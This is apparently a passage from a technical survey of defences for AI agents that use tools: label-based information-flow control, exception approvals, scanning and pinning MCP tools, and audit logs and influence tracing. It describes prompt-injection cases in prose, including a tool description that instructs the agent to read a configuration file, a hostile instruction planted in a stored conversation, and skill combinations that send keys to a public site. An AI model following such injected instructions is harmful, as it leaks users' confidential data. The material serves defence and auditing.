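Because anything in a model's context may influence what it writes next, ChainCaps keeps a budget for the context as a whole. Each time a value enters the context, the context's budget shrinks to its intersection with that value's budget, and everything the model writes afterwards inherits that smaller budget. When Jiang and colleagues turned this mechanism off in replayed runs, the share of attacks blocked fell by seven percentage points.

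This caution also blocks legitimate work. Once the model has read the salaries, the agent can't email the managers, even to tell them the report will be late. The order of calls can also matter. If the manifest for `fetch_url` treats a web request as a sink, an agent that opens the spreadsheet first can't fetch the public pay data. The model would write the web address with the salaries in its context, and the salaries' budget doesn't allow web requests. Fetching the page first avoids the problem.

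Costa and colleagues measured how much work such caution blocks on AgentDojo, the benchmark also used to test SPA and TACIT. With GPT-4o and no attacks, the agents completed these shares of the tasks:

| Type of task | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent, with label checks | Fides, with label checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
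| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

No prompt injection succeeded against any agent with the checks, while 152 succeeded against the ordinary agent without them. But the checks also stopped the ordinary agent from completing about half of the office tasks and most of the banking and Slack tasks. Some of these failures are unavoidable under the policy. For example, several banking tasks require the agent to follow instructions in a file, which the policy is meant to prevent.

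Fides recovers some of the lost tasks by keeping data out of the context. If a tool returns data with a stricter label than the context has, Fides stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass that name to another tool without reading the contents. It can also query a quarantined model about the contents and limit the form of the answer. A yes-or-no answer carries only one bit, so a policy might let the agent act on it even if it came from an untrusted page. The drawback is that models can mishandle the variables, as GPT-4o often did in the travel tasks. With the stronger model o1, Fides completed 68% of those tasks.

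Hiding data doesn't help if the agent has to read it to decide what to do next. In that case, APPA lets the agent open a temporary branch, which starts with a copy of the conversation and its labels. The branch reads the risky data and returns only a few values in a form the agent fixed in advance, such as a ticket number and a severity level. The software then discards the branch's conversation, so hostile text in it never reaches the main agent. The branch may still return a false value in the right form. Even a single number can reveal a secret, so whoever writes the policy has to decide what the returned values may be used for.

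Labels also build up over time, which is known as label creep. In Microsoft's version of Fides, one untrusted document makes the rest of the run untrusted unless the developer removes it from the context. ChainCaps can reset the context's budget when a new task begins, which is safe only if the model's context is also cleared. On a set of difficult but harmless tasks, the reset cut the share wrongly blocked from 45% to 20%. The high completion rates in the main test came from easier tasks than these.

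Dividing work among several agents can slow label creep, because each agent has its own context. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) simulated this without language models, using thousands of random tasks with up to 20 tool calls. The simulations measured the share of calls that either introduced sensitive data or ran in a context that already contained some. That share fell when there were more agents, when agents could pass data directly to one another instead of through a coordinator, and when only a few agents handled the sensitive tools. But more direct connections also meant more channels to monitor, and no arrangement removed the problem. Separate contexts can't help if a single agent must read the salaries and then write to the managers.

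### Exceptions and who answers for them

Because labels only become stricter, some legitimate tasks need an exception. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) distinguishes two kinds. Declassification permits a particular release of sensitive data, such as sending the median salary to the managers. Endorsement lets the agent treat selected untrusted data as trusted for a particular purpose, such as following the instructions in a supplier's email.

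Kravchenko and colleagues prove that once a call fails because its data is too confidential or too untrusted, the agent can't make it succeed by reading more data. Someone has to authorise the call, or trusted software has to transform the data, for example by removing names.

ChainCaps authorises an exception with a signed token that works once, for one call and the data behind it, so the agent can't reuse it for another recipient. APPA similarly ties each approval to the exact text of a call and records it in a log. The approval doesn't change the data's labels, so the next email needs a new approval. The approver can be a person, a fixed rule or another model, but a person has to set limits in advance on what each approver may permit and answer for the result.

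In a test of 20 simulated office workflows with three models, agents using APPA completed 87% to 91% of the tasks, and none of the attacks succeeded. Completion depended heavily on whether agents could recover from a blocked call. With GPT-5.6 Luna, it fell to 35.0% when APPA no longer suggested how to resolve a block, and to 56.5% without temporary branches. Versions of Fides that Kravchenko and colleagues configured themselves completed only 36% to 46% of the tasks, and 26% to 35% of attacks succeeded. But these versions lacked several rules the test required, such as limits on exact recipients, so we can't conclude much about Fides in general from the comparison.

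Frequent exceptions would bring back the approval prompts that labels were supposed to reduce. Kolluri and colleagues addressed this with Prudentia, a version of Fides that shows the model the labels and rules so it can plan around them. The model can also request one endorsement in place of many approvals. If an email lists 10 jobs, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving 10 separate calls. On AgentDojo with the model o4-mini, the number of requests to a person fell from 36.8 with Fides to 19.2 with Prudentia, while task completion stayed similar (75.7% and 73.2%).

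A mistaken endorsement does more damage than a mistaken approval, however, because the agent can act on everything in the email without asking again. The experiment assumed that people would catch every harmful request, but the volunteers in Hossain and colleagues' study often missed them. Labels could make the decision easier by showing what the older prompts left out. The prompt for the salary report could show that the text draws on the salary spreadsheet and that the managers don't have access to that spreadsheet.

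Kolluri and colleagues left general declassification out of Prudentia because whether a release is appropriate depends on the situation, and they preferred to ask about each call. *Agent libOS* cites a way to make exceptions more precise by specifying what someone may release, who may release it, where and when. For the monthly report, the head of HR might allow the company's median salary, but no other figure, to go to the managers' list once a month.

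The content needs checking even when the channel is allowed. *DelegateGuard* (2026), which tests permissions that agents pass to each other, includes attacks that send a secret through a legitimate channel visible to outsiders. It concludes that permissions must be combined with declassification rules or monitoring of outgoing data. For the monthly report, trusted software could calculate the median and release only that number, so that the model never writes the email from the full table. The head of HR would still have to consider what several releases reveal together, since two harmless averages revealed one person's pay when combined.

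## What an audit needs from tool definitions and run records

ChainCaps blocks the salary email only if the manifest for `read_file` is right, and Fides blocks it only if someone has labelled the spreadsheet. An auditor therefore has to check the tools before anyone installs them and whenever they change. After a run, the auditor also needs a record of what the agent did and which data it used.

### What a reviewer can read before installation

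The definition of `send_email` shows a reviewer that the agent chooses the recipient and the text. It doesn't show whether the server keeps a copy of each message or adds a hidden recipient, as the compromised Postmark server did. A DADL file shows more, because Declarative Closure lets a reader list every endpoint its tools can address.

An audit needs to check tool descriptions separately because the model reads them as soon as the client loads the list of tools. *A Remote MCP Server Can Rug Pull You* (Totten, 2026) gives the example of a description containing an instruction to read a configuration file before using any other tool. The agent may follow that instruction even if it never calls the described tool.

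A reviewer who can get the source code can answer some of the remaining questions. Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, collected all 21,643 servers in the public MCP registry in August 2026 and obtained code for about two-thirds of them. A scanner searched that code for known patterns of weakness and found no openly hostile tool descriptions, but it recovered tool definitions from only 4,238 of the 13,051 repositories and would miss a disguised instruction.

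The scanner also raised many false alarms. Kraishan checked 294 of its findings by hand, and 56% were real. The share was 93% for software dependencies without a fixed version, which a pattern can identify directly. It was 17% for code that might let outsiders run commands, because the risk depends on what the program later does with a piece of text.

### Scanning for dangerous combinations

Xie and colleagues found that skills that are harmless on their own can be dangerous together. *Scan Before You Install* (Gandhi, Aviv and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a backup skill that copies passwords and keys into a shared folder, and a debugging skill that uploads recent files from that folder to a public site.

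Their scanner looks for such combinations in five steps:

1. It extracts the files, environment variables and other skills that each skill uses.
2. It draws a graph with an arrow wherever one skill's output can reach another.
3. A language model proposes arrows that the code doesn't show, such as text that the agent would carry from one skill to the next in its context.
4. Fixed rules search for dangerous paths, such as one from sensitive data to a skill that sends data out.
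5. A model checks each path against quoted passages from the skills and drops any path without evidence.

Gandhi and colleagues tested the scanner on 1,325 sets of skills, mostly from the benchmark that Xie and colleagues built. The scanner found 665 of the 668 dangerous sets and wrongly flagged nine of the 657 others. A language model that read the same skills without a graph found 657 of the dangerous sets but wrongly flagged 362 of the others.

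These results depend heavily on the models inside the scanner. On 485 of the sets, the version without a model found 54.7% of the dangerous combinations with no false alarms. Adding the model's arrows increased detection to 99.2%, with false alarms on 7.0% of the safe sets. The final check reduced false alarms to 2.4% but also lowered detection to 95.4%.

The scanner found two dangerous combinations among 1,587 skills from 75 popular GitHub repositories. One joins a skill that retrieves old conversations to a skill that posts on Slack. The two share no files and neither calls the other, so the proposed link between them came only from the model. When the researchers planted a hostile instruction in an old conversation, GPT-5.2-Codex followed it in 2 of 12 runs and GLM-5 in 7 of 12. The other combination let an attacker steal an access token. The scanner had found nothing wrong with any of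 the four skills individually.

Two findings don't show that such combinations are rare, because nobody has checked the whole collection by hand. The scanner's misses are better known for single skills. Independent analysts reviewed 52 skills in full and found nine weaknesses. The scanner had found eight of these but missed one in which text downloaded during installation became standing instructions for later sessions. It reads skills without running them, so it can't examine text or code that arrives later.

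If `read_file` and `send_email` were skills and the scanner's policy listed the spreadsheet as sensitive, the scanner would flag the pair. The employer would still have to decide whether the managers may see the salaries.

### When an approved tool changes

A company that installs a server on its own machines can keep the copy it reviewed, but the operator of a remote server can change its descriptions or code at any time. Security researchers call it a rug pull when a server becomes malicious after gaining trust. *MCP-38* (2026), a threat catalogue, lists rewritten descriptions, requests redirected to an attacker's server, and altered code behind an unchanged interface.

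Ordinary changes are common too. Kraishan compared registry entries for 8,900 servers that had published more than one version. For 40.6% of these servers, the description or another detail such as the destination had changed but the identifiers had not, and 370 servers had moved to a different host. Kraishan expects most of these moves to be routine, but a client can't distinguish a routine move from a takeover. The registry doesn't store tool definitions, so these figures exclude changes to the tools themselves.

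An update can also change what an old call does. *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning* (2026) examined GitHub's MCP server, which lets an agent create a code repository by giving only a name. Version 1.3 makes the repository public by default, and version 1.4 makes it private. If an agent prepares the call for version 1.4 and the operator then returns to version 1.3, the same call publishes the code.

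Other updates don't change how old calls work but allow new ones. *SchemaCaps* (2026), which compared 565 pairs of successive releases, found a mobile-automation server that had added arguments for local file paths to 37 tools. A test that only repeated the old calls wouldn't reveal the new access to files.

Companies can watch for changes with methods such as pinning and hashing. Pinning means the client accepts only the approved version. A hash is a short fingerprint calculated from data, and even a one-character change almost certainly produces a different hash.

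| Control | What it can detect | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Pinned version number | a new release | changes that the operator makes without a new number |
| Hash of the tool definition | any change to the name, description or schema | different code behind the same definition |
| Hash of a local server's code | any change to that code | changes in an outside service that the code contacts |
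| Repeated test calls | different answers to those calls | different behaviour with other inputs |
| Renewed approval | a change that the reviewer recognises as risky | a change that the reviewer doesn't see or understand |

*ProbeID* (2026) shows why an audit can't rely on version numbers alone. It sent the same test calls to 16 servers over 77 days. Seven tools began to answer differently, although every server still reported its original version. One other tool seemed to change only because the researchers' own machine had changed. A company can repeatedly call `read_file` on a sample file, but testing `send_email` sends real messages unless the server offers a test mode.

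MCP doesn't require clients to check whether a tool's definition has changed since it was approved, and *ChainWatch* (2026) points out that it gives them no built-in way to detect such a change. In the July 2026 version, clients can subscribe to notices that a server's tool list has changed, but a dishonest server can choose not to send them. Separate software can help detect such changes. *MCP-DPT* (2026) describes MCP-Scan, which pins trusted tools and scans their descriptions. Totten, whose company Zuplo sells a gateway for MCP servers, conceded in June 2026 that the gateway did not yet pin definitions automatically.

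Asking for approval after every change may be practical for a small set of servers. In *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly*, Bharti (2026) measured about two description changes a day per 1,000 servers in the registry. At that rate, a company with 20 servers would see one roughly every 25 days. The live tool definitions may change more often, since Bharti measured only the short descriptions in the registry.

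Bharti found that re-reviewing the 5% of servers that had changed most in the past caught only about 20% of the known servers whose descriptions changed next. Bharti instead recommends a review whenever a description's hash changes, plus regular checks of the whole catalogue. Kraishan wants clients to ask for consent again when a server moves to another host, and the registry to publish the differences between versions. A reviewer who sees only the new file-path arguments has much less to read than one who gets all 37 definitions again.

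### What a run record must hold

MCP doesn't require anyone to keep an audit log of tool calls, so the company has to decide what to record. For the salary email, a useful record might look like this:

```json
{
  "call_id": "call_4",
  "time": "2026-12-01T09:14:06Z",
  "tool": "send_email",
  "parent_program": "pay_report_run_118",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "managers@example.com",
    "body": "Our median salary is 4% below the industry figure."
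  },
  "result": "accepted by mail server",
  "tool_version": "2.3.0, definition hash 9f2c71",
  "acting_user": "j.lee, through pay-agent",
  "permission": "rule 4: ask; approved by m.ortiz",
  "data_origins": [
    "call_1: /finance/pay/2026.csv",
    "call_2: https://stats.example.org/pay"
  ]
}
```

The log needs one such record for every primitive call, because the program's text also includes branches that never ran. Each missing piece leaves a different question open:

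| Missing information | Question that the auditor can't answer |
|---|---|
| The primitive call | Did the program send an email at all? |
| Parent program | Which other calls belonged to the same report? |
| Arguments | Who was the email for, and what did it say? |
| Result | Did the mail server accept it? |
| Tool version | What did the tool do with these arguments at the time? |
| Acting user | Did the agent act for someone who may open the spreadsheet? |
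| Permission decision | Did a rule or a person allow the email? |
| Data origins | Could the text have drawn on the salary spreadsheet? |

The tool version matters most when a call relies on defaults. If a log records only that an agent created a GitHub repository with a given name, an auditor can't tell from the log whether the repository was public.

OpenTelemetry, an open standard for tracking work as it passes between programs, can link a call to its parent program. It calls the whole run a trace and each operation within it a span, and a span can include its parent's identifier. The Model Context Protocol (2026) project's July changelog documents how MCP requests can carry trace and span identifiers. A gateway that receives them can group the calls from one program, which it can't do with the required fields alone. The July version also begins to phase out MCP's own logging feature and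 recommends OpenTelemetry instead. But these conventions don't cover recording who gave approval or where the data came from.

The client or broker can record most of this information as it forwards each call, but data origins are harder to record. ChainCaps and Fides can supply possible origins. Without such a system, the auditor has to infer them afterwards.

### Why a log of calls doesn't show influence

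Because the model can rephrase what it reads, the email may share no words with the spreadsheet. A source can also influence a call without contributing to its text. Suppose the page of public pay data advises companies to tell all managers about pay gaps at once. The agent might email the managers because of that advice, even though the message contains nothing from the page.

*From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 71 works, represents a run as a provenance graph, in which points are pieces of data or actions and arrows show how they relate. Software can log directly that a tool received a file or produced a result, but it usually can't log that a result changed the model's decision, because that depends on what the model would have done without that result.

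Let *R* be the actual run, and let *R*′ be the same run with neutral text in place of one source. The source influenced a call if

the call is missing from *R*′, or its arguments differ from those in *R*.

The direct test is to run the agent again with the neutral text. Because runs vary, an auditor would need several runs with each version of the text, using a simulated `send_email` to avoid sending more messages.

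More detailed logs don't remove the need for this test, and the survey recommends spending money on the ability to replay runs instead of recording every token. The model's written reasoning doesn't replace the test either, since it may cite a passage the model didn't use or omit one it did. A passage can also influence an action without justifying it, as when a false figure on a web page causes the agent to send an email.

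### Reconstructing influence with NeuroTaint

Cai, Wen and Tang (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, present NeuroTaint, which looks for influence after a run has finished. It first builds a graph of the run, including anything the agent stored in memory and retrieved in a later session. For each sink, such as an email, it then compares the outgoing text with the sources that could have reached it:

1. It looks for a unique marker that it added to the source when the agent read it.
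2. It measures how much wording the two texts share.
3. It compares their meanings using embeddings.
4. It repeats the comparison with small parts of the source, in case one relevant paragraph sits in a long page.

If none of these checks finds a match, NeuroTaint prompts a language model to predict whether the agent would have made the same call with neutral text in place of the source. This takes less compute than running the agent again, but it doesn't show what the agent would actually have done. The model also outputs a confidence score, which nobody has calibrated.

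Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on 400 scenarios that they wrote for 20 agent frameworks. In half of them, a source was meant to influence a sink. NeuroTaint detected 187 of these 200 cases and raised 16 false alarms in the other 200, for a recall of 93.5% and a precision of 92.1%. Fides detected 108 and raised 106 false alarms. However, Fides is designed to block unsafe calls during a run, so this comparison doesn't measure how well it protects an agent.

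Ten of NeuroTaint's 13 misses involved text whose meaning had become hard to match, usually after repeated rephrasing or storage in memory. In the other three, the source had changed the agent's decision but left little trace in the text. Most false alarms came from outputs that covered the same topic as a source or contained facts the model already knew. The salary agent could trigger a false alarm by opening a web page on industry pay and then writing about the subject from general knowledge.

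False alarms would probably make up a larger share of alarms in ordinary work, where influence may be much rarer than in the benchmark. If a source influenced the sink in only 5% of cases and NeuroTaint's error rates stayed the same, about 38% of its alarms would be correct. A second review can help remove false alarms. When Claude Opus 4.6 judged which of the 203 flagged cases were unsafe, it rejected all 16 false alarms and kept 179 of the 187 correct ones.

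NeuroTaint's recall also fell to 54.7% when the audited agent was Claude Opus 4.6. Cai and colleagues suggest that the stronger model stopped some attacks before they reached a sink. The benchmark still counted those scenarios as positive, so the lower figure mixes NeuroTaint's misses with attacks that never succeeded.

An audit with this method takes only 0.25 seconds per run on average, but it needs a full log that includes the agent's intermediate reasoning and memory operations. A company that records only the names and times of tool calls can't use the method later.

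### Records that others can trust without seeing everything

An outside auditor also needs to know that nobody has altered the log. Wang and colleagues found no evidence of protection against tampering in the published descriptions of the tracing systems they reviewed. Their survey doesn't cover every system, but it suggests that auditors often have to trust whoever runs the agent.

One safeguard is to include the previous record's hash in each new record and give the latest hash to an outside party. If the company later deleted the record of the salary email, the remaining hashes would no longer match. The hashes can't show that the original record was complete or listed the data's origins correctly.

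Full records create a privacy problem. The result of `read_file` contains the whole salary table, so logging it gives everyone who can read the log access to the salaries. The company could store a hash of the table instead. An auditor could then confirm that a saved copy of the table matches what the agent read, but couldn't recover the figures if nobody had kept a copy. A plain hash also does little to protect a single salary, because someone could hash every plausible salary and look for a match.

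Wang and colleagues recommend limits on what companies record, who can read it and how long they keep it. They also propose protecting the structure of a log separately from its contents, so that an outsider can detect missing or reordered calls without seeing the arguments. However, the auditor may need the hidden contents.

For the salary report, the company could keep the figures and the email text in a separate store with the same access rules as the spreadsheet, and delete them after a fixed period. An auditor could then still see from the remaining log that an email based on the spreadsheet may have gone to the managers, but could no longer check whether it revealed anyone's pay.
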